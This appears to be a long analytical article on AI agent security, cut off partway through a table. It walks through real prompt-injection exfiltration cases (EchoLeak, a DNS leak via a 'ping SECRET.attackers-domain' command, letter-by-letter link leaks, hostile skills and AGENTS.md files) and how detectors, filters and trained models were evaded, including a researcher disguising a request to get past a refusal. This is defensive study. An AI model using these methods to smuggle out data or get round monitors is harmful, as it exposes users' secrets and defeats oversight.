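Li and colleagues staged four attacks. In three, the hostile instructions were in a shared data file, in a temporary folder that several users' jobs could reach, or in the output of a compromised tool. In the fourth, two agents cooperated to move data out. AEGIS detected each attack in all three trials, typically half a second after it began. On recordings of the same attacks, a network data-loss prevention tool caught two of the four, as did file auditing and a strict sandbox. A monitor that judged each agent by its usual behaviour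 caught none. Li and colleagues built these tools themselves, so commercial products might do better.

The verifier added little overhead, using under 0.055% of processor time at the default setting. A stress test that only read files ran 28% slower, which Li and colleagues treat as an upper bound. In simulated workloads, the overhead grew from 1.1% with 10 agents to 4% with 500. AEGIS raised no false alarms, but the test covered only 42 legitimate actions.

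It is less clear how much AEGIS stopped, because it reacts to violations rather than preventing them. In the live tests of the four attacks, the agents had sent a median of 68, 50, 519 and 503 bytes before detection. In the controlled tests, the same attacks sent 68, 50, 519 and 521 bytes in total, so in at least three of them the attacker had probably received everything before the alarm. AEGIS could still cut short the theft of a large dataset, but it may not react in time to protect a password, which fits easily into 50 bytes.

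The results also depend heavily on the profile. The rule on network destinations caught the attack through the temporary folder, and the attack through the shared data file broke both that rule and a rule on folders. An attacker who stayed within the permitted folders, used a permitted connection and kept below the volume limit would break no rule. Li and colleagues acknowledge that anything the profile leaves open does not count as a violation. Protection therefore depends largely on how well someone can write the list of permitted destinations, and three published leaks show how hard that is.

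### EchoLeak: a permitted service that forwards

After the email passed Microsoft's classifier, Aim Labs still needed a way to get data out, since Copilot could not send mail. The group had Copilot end its answer with a web link containing the most sensitive information Copilot could find. Copilot normally removed outside links, but only if they were written in the usual way. Markdown, the markup language Copilot uses to format its answers, also allows a link to have a label in the text and its address at the bottom, and Copilot did not remove links written this way.

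A link works only if the user clicks on it, so the group turned it into an image, which a browser fetches automatically. Egress control blocked the image request. Copilot's page had a content security policy, which lists the domains from which the browser may load images, and the attacker's domain was not on the list.

So the group went through the list. In SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, they found a function that would fetch an outside address on request, but the user first had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a similar function in Microsoft Teams that needed no invitation. The browser requested an image from Teams, and Teams forwarded the request to the attacker's server with the secret in the address. The browser connected only to permitted domains.

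*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) dates Aim Labs' report to January 2025 and Microsoft's fix to May, and cites no evidence that anyone used the attack. Ravia writes that, as far as the group knows, no customer setting would have prevented it. He heads a research team at a company that sells protection for AI systems, but his claim is plausible because Microsoft controlled both the filter and the list.

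The same weakness came back a year later, in June 2026, when the security firm Varonis published SearchLeak, an attack on the enterprise version of Copilot. The attack started when the user clicked a link containing a hidden prompt. An image in Copilot's answer then loaded before Copilot had finished cleaning up the answer, and the data left through Bing's image search, which was on the list and could fetch outside addresses. According to TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one click data theft tool*, the data at risk included the user's inbox and stored files. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it.

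### The DNS leak: a harmless command that carries data

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, asks the user before it runs most commands. In 2025, it skipped this step for a list of commands deemed safe. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* describes how a security researcher found the list in the program's source code and asked Claude which entries an attacker could misuse. Claude picked four, including `ping`, which tests whether another computer is reachable.

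Before a computer can contact another by name, it has to look up the name in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's address book. The query passes from server to server until it reaches one that the domain's owner controls. If the agent runs `ping SECRET.attackers-domain`, with a real password in place of `SECRET`, the password appears in the attacker's server log. This works even if the `ping` itself doesn't get through, because the lookup has already delivered the data.

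The injection in the source code file instructed Claude Code to extract an access key from a settings file and put it into the domain name. Claude refused until the researcher disguised which file he wanted. It also refused to contact domains well known from security testing, but accepted one that was not. Anthropic received the report on 26 May 2025 and fixed the flaw by 6 June. The official description, reproduced in INCIBE's *CVE-2025-55284* (2025), attributes the flaw to "an overly broad allowlist of safe commands".

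A firewall that blocks unknown websites might not have helped, because DNS is a separate channel that most networks leave open. Zenity Labs' *It's Always DNS in Claude’s Sandbox* describes a related gap in another Anthropic product, where filters blocked unapproved web traffic but the DNS lookup happened before they could act.

### The web-fetch leak: data in the choice of link

The third leak got past a much more careful rule. Claude's chat product can open web pages, and it keeps facts about its user from earlier conversations. To stop an attacker from getting Claude to write those facts into a web address, Anthropic let it open only addresses that the user had typed or that had appeared in earlier search results or fetched pages. Willison quotes Anthropic's developer documentation, which warned that some risk remained.

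Willison (2026) describes how Ayush Paul exploited the last part of the rule in July 2026. Paul built a website that required AI assistants to identify themselves, supposedly to prevent abuse, by looking up their user's name in a directory one letter at a time. The first page had a link for each letter, and each link led to another page of links. Claude spelled out the user's name by following these links, without writing any address of its own, and Paul's server recorded its choices. He also obtained the user's home city and employer. Only visitors that identified themselves as Claude saw these pages, which made the trap harder to discover.

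Anthropic said it already knew about the problem, and it paid no reward. It has since fixed the problem by stopping the tool from following links in the pages it fetches.

The trick was already known. After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to a web address. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how an attacker could then supply a complete address for each letter, each digit and the space, and have ChatGPT open them in the order that spelled out the data. Radware reported this in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it that December.

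An agent using this channel reveals log₂ N bits each time it chooses one of N links, so with 37 addresses each request reveals about 5.2 bits, or one character. That is far too slow to leak a contract, but a name or a password takes only about a dozen requests. Forbidding the agent to write addresses slows the leak. To stop it completely, a designer must also ensure that the agent's choices do not depend on anything secret, or that the attacker cannot see them.

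### What a tighter rule would have to specify

In all three cases the rule named something as safe, a domain, a command or a link, and the attacker used it to carry data. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) reaches a similar diagnosis from eleven real attacks on agents, including the DNS leak. It classes every one of them as a failure to control where information flows, and most of them as a failure of some other principle too. A list of names cannot do that job alone. A better rule would also have to cover:

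- **The part of the site.** Claude Code once treated all of Hugging Face, a site where anyone can publish models, as approved. According to Vulners' *CVE-2026-54316 Claude Code*, this included pages that an attacker controlled. Willison, in *The Summer of Johann*, lists similar cases in which OpenAI had approved cloud domains where anyone can rent storage or a server. For services with accounts, the rule also has to say which account.
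- **What the service does with a request.** Teams and Bing were both trustworthy hosts, but each would fetch an address for a stranger. Many ordinary sites also redirect visitors elsewhere.
- **Every way out.** This includes DNS and the arguments of a command, since `ping` is harmless with one name and a leak with another.
- **Who chose the address, and from how many.** An address that the user typed reveals nothing new. One that the agent picked from a stranger's list may reveal a character of a password.

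OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a tighter rule than a list of trusted sites. The agent may open an address automatically only if a separate web crawler, with no access to users' conversations, has already seen that exact address in public. Otherwise, the agent has to find a different source or the user has to approve. An address containing somebody's private details will almost never be in the crawler's index. OpenAI rejected lists of trusted sites partly because a trusted site can redirect the agent elsewhere, and partly because strict lists produce so many warnings that people click through them without thinking.

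This would have stopped the original ShadowLeak request, but it is less clear whether it would stop data being spelled out letter by letter. As OpenAI describes it, the rule checks each address separately, so an attacker could perhaps publish the 37 pages, wait for the crawler to find them, and then use each page to stand for one character. OpenAI promises only that the agent will not quietly leak data through the address itself, and treats the check as one layer among several.

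The surest rule, and a much blunter one, is to give an agent no outside connection while it handles private files. Willison (2025) uses the term "lethal trifecta" for a system that combines private data, exposure to hostile text and a way to send data out. EchoLeak needed all three, and so did the other leaks described here. Cutting the outside connection removes the third, so nobody has to recognise an attack. But it also removes much of what people want agents for. Even Anthropic's narrow fix gets in the way of useful work, since following a link from one page to the next is an ordinary part of research.

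### The two emails again

Egress control can stop case A if the mail tool enforces it. The assistant steals the files by forwarding them in an email. A firewall sees only a connection to the company's own mail server, which it has to allow, but the mail tool can check the recipient's address. If the tool sends mail only to colleagues and known business contacts, the theft fails even though the injection has completely fooled the assistant.

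The attacker would then look for another way to get data out, such as an image in the summary that the assistant shows its owner. The same restrictions must therefore apply to everything the assistant can cause to be sent, including requests from the owner's browser. Even then, the rule fails if the attacker has taken over the mailbox of a supplier on the list.

In case B, neither inspection nor egress control can detect or stop the fraud, because the payment goes through the company's own bank. Shortening the list of allowed destinations would not help unless the company removed that bank from it. A rule that allowed payments only to account numbers already on file would stop the fraud, but the payment tool would have to enforce it, and someone would have to update the file whenever a supplier really changed banks.

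## Can endpoint detection be extended to agents?

Endpoint detection and response (EDR) records parts of an attack that never appear in network traffic. In case A, it would log the assistant's process opening the contract files and then connecting to the mail server. It would not log the email that caused this or the owner's request, which was only for a summary. Without those two texts, the log would look the same if the owner had asked the assistant to send the contract to a colleague.

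Li, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *ADR*, give a similar example. A developer asks an agent to summarise a ticket from a work-tracking system, and the agent reads the developer's SSH keys (credentials for logging in to other machines) and sends a web request. EDR can see the file access and the connection, but only a comparison with the original request shows that something is wrong. Their system, Agentic AI Detection and Response (ADR), had run for over ten months on MacBooks at Uber when they published. It is the strongest case so far for extending endpoint detection to agents. (This is not the team that built AEGIS, whose first author is also called Li.)

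### How ADR works

Coding agents such as Cursor, Cline and Claude Code record their sessions in databases and log files on the user's computer. Once an hour, ADR's sensor reads these records and joins the scattered entries into complete sessions, which contain the user's prompts, the agent's written reasoning, and each tool call with its arguments and result. The sensor also lists the installed software packages and the MCP servers available to the agent. MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a common standard for connecting agents to outside tools, and an MCP server is a program that offers them.

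A company could instead put a gateway between the agent and everything it contacts. Li and colleagues decided against this because a gateway requires changes to the agent software, does not work with streamed responses and misses context such as installed packages.

The sessions then go through a two-stage detector. In triage, one language model reads everything and passes on whatever looks suspicious, such as typical injection phrases or requests that touch credentials. A second, more expensive model investigates these cases and can look up the source code of the tools involved, a collection of known attack techniques, and the company's security policies. Li and colleagues modelled this on a company's security staff, where one group screens alerts and another investigates the serious ones.

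ADR also has an offline part, the Explorer, which looks for new attacks before deployment. One agent proposes variants of known attacks, another runs them in a sandbox, and a third writes up the most useful ones for the collection that the second-stage model consults. Each variant gets a score:

F = ε × σ × τ^α

Here ε is how far the attack got, σ is how harmless it looked, and τ is how much damage it could do. Li and colleagues set α to 1.2, which gives damage slightly more weight. Because the factors are multiplied, a very damaging but obvious attack scores poorly. The highest-scoring variants survive and mutate again in the next round.

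### What it caught

Li and colleagues built their own benchmark, ADR-Bench, with 302 tasks that use 133 MCP servers and average 28.5 tool calls. Forty-two of the tasks are attacks, covering 17 techniques. ADR detected 28 of the attacks (67%) and raised no false alarms on the 260 benign tasks. Three other detectors each detected between 8 and 17 attacks and raised 30 to 40 false alarms. On 93 AgentDojo tasks, ADR detected every attack and raised three false alarms on the 55 benign tasks, a rate of 5.5%.

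On its own benchmark, ADR caught all nine attacks that got around security controls or disrupted operations, and 13 of the 19 in which the attacker first gained a foothold. But it caught only five of the nine that manipulated data or reasoning, the group closest to case B, and one of the five that abused permissions. These groups are very small, but it makes sense that a detector does worse when the agent is allowed to take every action in the attack.

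Triage also reduced detection more than its design suggests. Li and colleagues told the first model to escalate whenever it was in doubt. When they removed triage and sent everything to the second model, detection rose from 67% to about 80%, but this caused two false alarms and raised the cost from 2.4 to 3.1 cents per task.

With only 42 attacks, the true detection rate could plausibly be from about 50% to 80%. It could also be lower for unfamiliar attacks, because the collection the second model consults covers the same framework of techniques as the benchmark. Neither benchmark tests an attacker who adapts to ADR.

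In production, ADR covered over 7,200 computers and processed more than 10,000 sessions a day. It found hundreds of credentials that had left the company by accident. The injection attacks Li and colleagues describe from this period were exercises. In one, a malicious email automatically created a ticket with hidden instructions. When a developer's agent opened the ticket, it read local configuration files and sent credentials out. ADR reconstructed several stages of the attack. The deployment is therefore good evidence that ADR finds leaked secrets, but much weaker evidence that it finds hijacked agents.

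### An hour is too late to prevent anything

A session can wait up to an hour before the sensor collects it, or half an hour on average if sessions are spread evenly, and analysis then takes about 18 seconds. Even AEGIS, which typically reacted within half a second, had probably let small secrets escape by then. Li and colleagues report that credentials had often already left the company by the time ADR raised an alert. After a late alert, a company can still replace a leaked password, but it can't make a contract secret again once a competitor has read it.

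Uber therefore added a check that runs before the harm is done. Cursor and Claude Code offer hooks, which are points in the agent loop where an outside script can inspect or block what passes through. Uber's script searches each prompt for strings that resemble credentials before the agent receives it. Of the 212 strings it flagged, 206 were real credentials (97.2%), but that figure does not show how many credentials the script missed.

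The script uses fixed patterns and a measure of randomness, not a language model. Li and colleagues say such checks work for secrets with a recognisable format but fail when the decision depends on what a tool does or what the company permits. Neither test email needs to contain a credential, so this hook would not stop them.

### The agent helps to write the evidence

ADR relies on records that the agent software writes on the user's computer. An agent that can run commands with the user's permissions can often edit or delete the user's files, and an hour is plenty of time to do so. Unless the company protects these records separately, they don't meet the requirement that a reference monitor be tamper-proof. Conventional EDR and AEGIS both collect their data from the operating system, which is harder for an agent to alter.

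Even an intact record can mislead the detector, which is itself a language model and reads whatever the attacker wrote there. An injection could include, for instance, a false claim that the security team had approved the transfer, addressed to the detector. Li and colleagues mention attempts to influence the detector as a risk. Their precautions are to fix the versions of models and prompts and to rerun the benchmarks before each update. These guard against accidental changes in the detector more than against text an attacker has planted in the log.

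Defenders need to be especially careful with the agent's written reasoning, because after a forged-reasoning attack it might contain a fluent justification for the theft. The list of tool calls is better evidence, especially if a defender checks it against EDR data. If the EDR log shows a file access or connection with no matching tool call in the agent's record, that would be a good reason to raise an alarm, regardless of the agent's written reasoning.

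### How many false alarms a day?

ADR raised no false alarms in 260 benign tasks, but by the usual 95% standard its true false-alarm rate could still be as high as about 1.15%. If the tasks are independent, a system with that rate would have about a 5% chance of raising no false alarms in 260 tasks, since (1 − 0.0115)^260 ≈ 0.05. At 10,000 sessions a day, a 1.15% rate would produce about 115 false alarms daily, and the 5.5% rate from AgentDojo would produce about 550.

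Real sessions differ from benchmark tasks, so these figures are not forecasts, but the production data give a partial check. Of the alerts they reviewed, Uber's analysts labelled 49% as false, 34% as real incidents, and 17% as correct but harmless, mostly caused by Uber's own security testers. Many of the false alarms came from long, complicated sessions, such as analyses of large codebases. A security team can tolerate a roughly even split between correct and false alerts. But the most common real incidents were exposed credentials, and Li and colleagues describe most other kinds of attack as exceedingly rare. If ADR were used only to detect injections, false alarms would make up a far larger share of its alerts.

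How much larger depends on how often agents encounter injections. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) searched 1.2 billion addresses from Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for nearly 4,000 phrases typical of injections, then checked the matches. They confirmed injections on 9,676 pages, about one in 124,000. These pages belonged to 285 of the 24.8 million hosts in the sample.

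The most common template among these injections tells the model to return random numbers, and others promote a business or try to keep AI systems away from a site's content. Most of the injections do not attempt theft. Khodayari and colleagues also tested whether 13 models follow such instructions while summarising a page. Compliance peaked at 8%, for smaller models that received the page as plain text, and was about 1% or less when the page kept its structure.

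In a study published in April 2026, Google searched the same archive and came to a similar conclusion. It found mostly pranks, search-engine manipulation and attempts to deter AI agents, plus a few crude attempts to steal data or delete files. The malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google gave no absolute rate. Its search also produced many false alarms, because most pages that matched its search phrases were articles about prompt injection.

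If each of the 10,000 daily sessions read ten pages drawn at random from this archive, the agents would together read about 0.8 injected pages a day. Even if they followed 8% of these injections, an agent would be hijacked only about once every 15 days. Over those 15 days, a false-alarm rate of 1.15% would produce about 1,700 false alarms.

A company under deliberate attack would face more injections than this. Both studies looked for known phrases on public pages, and neither covers private mailboxes, where an attacker can choose a target. But the conclusion holds even at a much higher rate. If one session in 10,000 contained an attack and ADR caught two-thirds of attacks, it could raise no more than one false alarm per 15,000 sessions for half its alerts to be real. Demonstrating such a low rate would take about 45,000 benign sessions in a row without a false alarm, and ADR-Bench has 260.

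### Attacks spread over several sessions

ADR evaluates each session separately, so an attacker may try to spread an attack over several. For example, an agent might list files in one session, read a configuration file in another, summarise the credentials in it in a third, and send a "report" to an outside address in a fourth. Agents usually start each session with an empty context, so the attack has to persist elsewhere, such as in a saved memory, a shared file or a database entry. The secret may also become harder to recognise as it passes between sessions. A password might reappear as ordinary prose in a weekly digest and leave the company as an attachment in the next session.

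*Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents* tests detection of such attacks with two sets of 54 scenarios. In one set, a lot of other traffic dilutes the attack. For the other, a program also softened the wording, and 12 of its scenarios reveal nothing when a detector sees each session in isolation. A Claude model acted as the detector and received the material in different ways:

- When it judged each session separately, its detection rate fell by about half from the diluted set to the reworded one.
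- When it read the complete log of all sessions at once, the rate also fell by about half, although the log fitted easily into its context window.
- When a selection program passed on only the 50 most telling fragments, the rate held up on both sets.

Long storage therefore isn't enough. Uber keeps ADR's data for 13 months, but something still has to pick out the fragments that belong together. Reading the whole log at once is also risky, because harmless-looking pieces from separate sessions can combine into an injection against the detector. However, the evidence is thin. The tests used one family of models and first-draft prompts, and the author, who works at Intrinsec AI, presents the results as only a rough characterisation.

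The same work offers a mathematical argument for reading prompts instead of the logs that most security tools analyse. Let G be the attacker's goal, P the incoming prompt, E what the agent then executes, and L the resulting log. If each depends only on the one before, the data processing inequality from information theory applies:

I(G; P) ≥ I(G; E) ≥ I(G; L)

I(G; P), the mutual information between goal and prompt, measures how much the prompt reveals about the goal. The log can therefore never reveal more about the goal than the prompt does. This limit applies when the attacker types the prompts. But in an indirect injection, the owner's prompt is harmless and the attacker's text arrives later, in a tool result, so the chain does not hold. A detector also has to read the tool results, as ADR does.

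### Agents the company does not know about

ADR's sensor can only read records in formats it supports. Employees also run agents that their company never approved, including homemade scripts of a few dozen lines that no software inventory lists. In *Detecting Shadow AI*, Canale and Soulis (2026) tested whether these agents leave enough traces on a Windows computer to be found.

A rule that flags any program that keeps a connection to a remote service and also runs commands would catch software installers and administrators' scripts as well as agents. Canale and Soulis therefore compared agents with "behavioural twins", the same programs connected to a service unrelated to AI. Two rules based only on behaviour flagged every twin.

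Their own tool, Agent Detector, also checks which service is at the other end of the connection. It combines a catalogue of 184 entries for language-model services with evidence from configuration files, installed software and Windows' record of programs that have run. In five runs with 12 synthetic agents, it flagged no twins and found each agent in most of the runs.

Its main weakness is again timing. Many AI providers share a content-delivery network with unrelated websites, so an IP address alone does not identify them. Agent Detector has to find the provider's name in the computer's list of recent lookups, where it stays for only one to five minutes. The tool normally scans once an hour. It detected an agent that worked intermittently in about one scan in three, and it missed very short-lived agents altogether. A scan takes only about 154 milliseconds, so a company could run it much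 more often. More frequent scans would still miss agents in WSL 2, a Linux environment inside Windows, and agents in a provider's cloud, which leave no trace on the laptop.

Canale and Soulis ran every trial on one workstation and say the test is too small to rank detectors. Finding an agent doesn't show whether someone has hijacked it, but a company must find an agent before it can monitor the agent's sessions.

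### Skills and instruction files without malicious code

Agents increasingly load skills, which are folders of instructions, sometimes with scripts, that prepare the agent for a particular kind of task. Developers share them on public marketplaces. Snyk, a security company, scanned 3,984 skills from one marketplace and confirmed by human review that 76 were malicious. Some malicious skills work much like conventional malware. Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain* describes skills that made agents run a program to collect passwords and keys from more than 100 file locations and send them to an outside server. EDR has a fair chance of detecting such a program, because the program behaves the same way whether a person or an agent starts it.

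Other skills contain only text. Ox Security, which also sells security software, examined 542,207 open-source components for a November 2026 report. According to Infosecurity Magazine, none of the skills it flagged ran code on installation, but 26% contained prompt injection or tool poisoning (hostile text in a tool's description), and 44% contained instructions to send data out. These percentages cover only the skills Ox flagged, so they don't show how common such skills are overall.

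*Exploiting LLM Agent Supply Chains via Payload-less Skills* (Liu, Hu and colleagues, 2026) tested attacks that supply no code. The malicious skills describe the theft as a company procedure. One tells the agent to capture the "ambient node properties" and send them to a server whose address it spells out in words. The agent infers that "ambient node properties" means the environment variables, where developers often keep passwords and access keys, and writes the program to steal them.

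Liu and colleagues combined 12 such skills with 50 ordinary tasks and ran them on three agents (OpenClaw, Claude Code and Codex) with three models each. Complete data theft succeeded in 28% to 78% of attempts, depending on the agent and model. Skills meant to make the agent download and run a stranger's code succeeded in 3% to 67% of attempts. In many other attempts, the agent contacted the attacker's server but sent only harmless system details, because it misunderstood the skill's vague wording or withheld the secrets.

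Two scanners, SkillScan and LLM Guard, flagged none of the 12 skills, although they had flagged 92% and almost 100% of the skills from an earlier attack that hides code in the documentation. With so few skills, this result is compatible with a true detection rate of up to 22%. SkillScan searches for known patterns, and LLM Guard is a set of general-purpose classifiers, but a scanner that understood the text might well flag a skill that spells out a server address in words. Liu and colleagues propose having a separate language model compare what a skill asks for with the permissions it declares, but they did not test this.

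The theft becomes much easier to detect once the agent acts. The finished program reads all environment variables and sends them to an unknown address, and EDR or egress control might stop it. Liu and colleagues acknowledge that they tested neither, and add that many people run these agents on private computers without such protection.

An attacker may not need a marketplace. Coding agents look for a file called AGENTS.md, in which developers leave instructions for them. TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware* reports that in October 2026 the security vendor Forever Security said it had found a malicious one in a customer's Downloads folder. The file looked like ordinary engineering notes but contained instructions to install a malicious package and steal session tokens. The vendor says it reproduced the attack on Codex and Claude Code. It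 could not establish how the file got there, but suspects that a compromised website made the browser save it, which needs no click.

Instruction files can be dangerous even when their authors mean well. Schneier on Security's *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* reports on a scan of 8,265 files that large companies publish to guide AI systems around their websites. Of these, 120 referred to software packages or domains that nobody had registered. The researchers registered a few of the names and published test packages, and within an hour a machine had run one. A scanner would have found nothing malicious in the original files, because the danger came from whoever registered the names later.

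Scanners that interpret a file's purpose can catch malicious files that signature matching misses. Google Cloud describes a malicious configuration file for a code editor that the engines on VirusTotal, a malware-scanning service, failed to detect for several days. VirusTotal's Code Insight feature flagged it because of what the configuration would make the editor do. Such a scanner still has to scan the right file at the right time. NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* describes a demonstration by the company's security team in which the hostile AGENTS.md file did not exist until a compromised software library wrote it during the agent's session. The file made Codex add a five-minute delay to a program, which an endpoint monitor would have recorded as an ordinary code edit. It also made Codex leave the change out of the summary it wrote for human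 reviewers.

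## Do AI firewalls and better-trained models hold against an attacker who adapts?

An AI firewall is a filter, usually a language model, that reads the text passing between an agent and its tools and blocks or rewrites anything suspicious. It sits where a network firewall would, but it evaluates what the text means, which network inspection and endpoint logging mostly don't do. The other approach is to train the agent's own model to ignore injected instructions. Both depend on a model distinguishing injections from ordinary text, and an attacker can keep rewording an injection until the model gets it wrong.

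### Two filters between the agent and its tools

Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, tested about the simplest version of the idea. The team, mostly from the software company ServiceNow and the Montreal research institute Mila, placed two language models at the boundary between agent and tools, each with a written prompt and no special training. In the office assistant, they would work like this:

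1. The assistant proposes a tool call, such as a file search.
2. A first filter, the Minimizer, receives the owner's request, the tool's description and the arguments of the call. It removes any private data that the task doesn't need.
3. The program runs the tool with what remains.
4. A second filter, the Sanitizer, receives the owner's request and the tool's result. It writes the result out again without anything that looks like an injection, and the assistant reads only this version.

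On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as the agent, 57.7% of attacks succeeded without a defence. The Sanitizer alone reduced this to 0%. Utility without attacks fell from 83% to 74%, but utility under attack rose from 50% to 69%, since a hijacked agent often fails to finish its owner's task.

The Minimizer alone was much less effective, reducing attack success to 18%, mainly by stopping thefts of private data. The Sanitizer alone had already reduced attack success to zero, so adding the Minimizer only lowered utility further, to 58%. The Minimizer sometimes removed details that the task required.

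Older filters often stop attacks by preventing the agent from doing much of its work. AgentDojo's own injection detector let 8% of attacks succeed and halved utility to 41%. On τ-bench, a benchmark of long conversational tasks to which the team added data-stealing attacks, a detector of this type stopped every attack but cut the share of tasks the agent completed from 52% to 7%. The Sanitizer avoided this loss of utility. Bhagwatkar and colleagues report that it never mistook harmless text for an attack, but they also traced two of the nine AgentDojo tasks that the agent repeatedly failed with the Sanitizer on to text it had wrongly removed.

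### What the score of zero measured

The paper's subtitle asks whether firewalls are all you need, or stronger benchmarks. Much of the paper argues for the benchmarks.

In some AgentDojo tasks, the injection overwrites something the agent needs, such as the amounts on a bill. The agent then fails the owner's task even if it ignores the attacker. In other tasks, the scoring code is too strict. If the agent sends the right summary to the right person but also sends that person a second message, the task counts as failed. Correcting these faults raised GPT-4o's utility under one type of attack from 61% to 72% with no defence.

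Another benchmark, Agent Security Bench, had a worse problem. It forced the attacker's tools into the agent's selection, then counted any use of them as a successful attack. When the team let the agent choose its own tools, the attack success rate fell from 74% to 9%. The original version is also the exception to the paper's claim of perfect security, since 16% of attacks succeeded despite the Sanitizer. A third benchmark, InjecAgent, doesn't measure utility, so a filter that deleted everything would get a perfect score.

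The bigger concern is that the attacks are too easy, because most use fixed tags and stock phrases that a language model readily recognises. Bhagwatkar and colleagues therefore built a three-stage attack in which each stage runs only if the earlier ones fail. The first stage uses AgentDojo's existing injections. The second uses seven templates that disguise the injected instruction as trustworthy metadata, sometimes next to an obviously malicious decoy. In the third, a language model that has been told about the defence rewrites the injection over ten rounds, drawing on earlier successes and failures.

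They ran this attack only on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. The attack's success rate against the Sanitizer was 0% after the first stage, 12.5% after the second and 30% after the third. Against PromptArmor, another filter, which asks a model to find the injection and then cuts out the matching text, the final rate was 75.5%, and most of PromptArmor's failures came from the templates. Bhagwatkar and colleagues think the Sanitizer does better because it rewrites the whole result and so depends less on finding a suspicious phrase.

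The paper describes the attacker's success against the Sanitizer as limited and stresses the extra effort the third stage requires. But ten rounds of rewriting is little work for an attacker, and a company whose assistant reads strangers' email all day may not consider a 30% success rate limited.

### An attacker with time and a budget

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025), by a group that includes researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, is the most thorough test of such defences. It tested twelve published defences, ten designed mainly against prompt injection and two against jailbreaks. Most of the original evaluations had reported attack success rates near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve.

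Their method is a loop. The attacker proposes some texts, tries them on the defended system, scores how close each one came to the goal, and uses the scores to write the next batch. Nasr and colleagues ran this loop in four ways:

- **Gradients.** The attacker uses the model's internal calculations to estimate which changes of wording would help. This works well on images but is still unreliable on text.
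- **Reinforcement learning.** A language model writes the attacks, and training adjusts it towards those that score well.
- **Search.** A language model makes variations on the best attacks so far, and the best of those survive to the next round, as in breeding.
- **People.** More than 500 participants attacked the defences in an online competition.

Two of the defences against prompt injection only change the prompt. Spotlighting marks untrusted text with special characters, and prompt sandwiching repeats the owner's request after the untrusted text to keep the model on task. AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded against them as little as 1% of the time, while the search succeeded over 95% of the time. One attack that beat sandwiching presented the malicious steps as a credential check that the agent had to complete before it could do what the owner wanted. Repeating the owner's request doesn't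 help against this attack, and may even make the agent more likely to complete the check.

Four of the defences were detectors, the type closest to an AI firewall. Search succeeded over 90% of the time against Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard and Google's Model Armor, and 71% of the time against PIGuard. One successful text was a short note saying that a new company policy required every rescheduled meeting to be logged by deleting a certain temporary file. It has the same form as the hostile installation step in a README. Nothing in its wording identifies it as an attack, and a detector strict enough to catch it would also flag many genuine office notices.

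MELON, another of the twelve, uses a method that the attacker isn't supposed to know about. It runs the agent twice, the second time with a harmless request to summarise what the tools returned. If a tool call appears in both runs, the owner's request can't have caused it, so MELON flags the tool results as containing an injection. The search got past MELON 76% of the time without information about how it worked. With that information, the success rate rose to 95%, because the search soon found a text instructing any system doing a summary to ignore the malicious instructions.

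The human participants collectively succeeded in all of a selected set of scenarios, while the automated search succeeded in 69% of them.

#### Why the fixed tests misled

A fixed list contains attacks written before the defence existed. Developers often train their defences on similar examples, so a good score may show only that the defence blocks attacks like those it was trained on. That is tolerable for most uses of machine learning, because future inputs will mostly resemble past ones. An attacker, however, chooses inputs that the defence lets through. Nasr and colleagues found that defences with near-zero attack success rates on public benchmarks were often among the easiest to break.

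Image-recognition researchers had learned this years earlier, when simple variants of known attacks kept defeating defences published at leading conferences. Nasr and colleagues conclude that testing can never prove a defence robust, and can show only that serious attempts to break it failed.

The attacker in these tests is unusually strong. It has plenty of computing power and, when attacking detectors, could see how confident the detector was about each attempt, which a criminal emailing a company would not. The results therefore show that these defences can be broken but give little indication of how much effort that would take. *AutoDojo* (2026) tests an attacker with fewer resources, which uses a small number of queries to a language model to improve the injection. With GPT-4o-mini as the agent, PIGuard blocked all of the fixed attacks but let 28.0% of the improved ones succeed. That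 is far below the earlier 71%, although the two tests differ in more than the attacker's resources. Some defences that enforce rules outside the model still gave protection under the same attack.

### Training the model itself

Before the current generation of models, researchers proposed several ways to train a model to keep instructions and data apart. The instruction hierarchy ranks the sources of text, with the operator above the user and the user above tool results, and trains the model to follow the higher-ranked source when instructions conflict. StruQ, short for structured queries, comes closest to the parameterised query that fixed SQL injection. It puts instructions and data in separate fields, divided by reserved markers that it removes from the data, and trains the model to ignore instructions in the data field. SecAlign trains the model on pairs of answers, one that follows the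 user and one that follows the injection, to prefer the first.

The resemblance to a parameterised query ends at the model, since the separation holds only as well as the model has learned it. Narisetty and colleagues collect the results of later tests, on a scale where 1 means that the attacker always gets their way:

- Ordinary combined attacks, with no adaptation at all, scored 0.68 and 0.75 on two benchmarks against GPT-4o-mini, which has been trained on the instruction hierarchy.
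- An attack that used gradients to optimise its wording scored between 0.80 and 1.00 against StruQ.
- The same method scored 0.88 against SecAlign on one benchmark and 0.46 on the other.

Nasr and colleagues got similar results. Their reinforcement-learning attack made a StruQ model output the attacker's phrase in every case they tried. One successful attack used text that opened like a system prompt, followed by an explanation that the software processing the answer expected a validation word on the first line. Against Meta SecAlign, a later version built for agents, the success rate rose from 2% with AgentDojo's fixed attacks to 96% with attacks found by search.

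Most of the attacks that beat the trained models imitated a system prompt. This is consistent with the role confusion that Ye and colleagues measured, in which a model gives a passage the authority of whoever it sounds like. Training on a list of injections teaches the model to reject text that imitates the sources on that list, but an attacker can imitate a different source. In image recognition, the training that helped generated new attacks against the model as it learned, but it protected only against attacks of the same type.

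### What the newest system cards report

Developers have kept training their models to resist injections, and results have improved a great deal. Some of the most detailed recent figures are in the system card for Claude Opus 5, the safety report Anthropic published with the model in July 2026. The table gives the results with extended thinking, a setting in which the model reasons at length before it acts.

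| Setting | Source of the attacks | Attempts per scenario | Success, model alone | Success with safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
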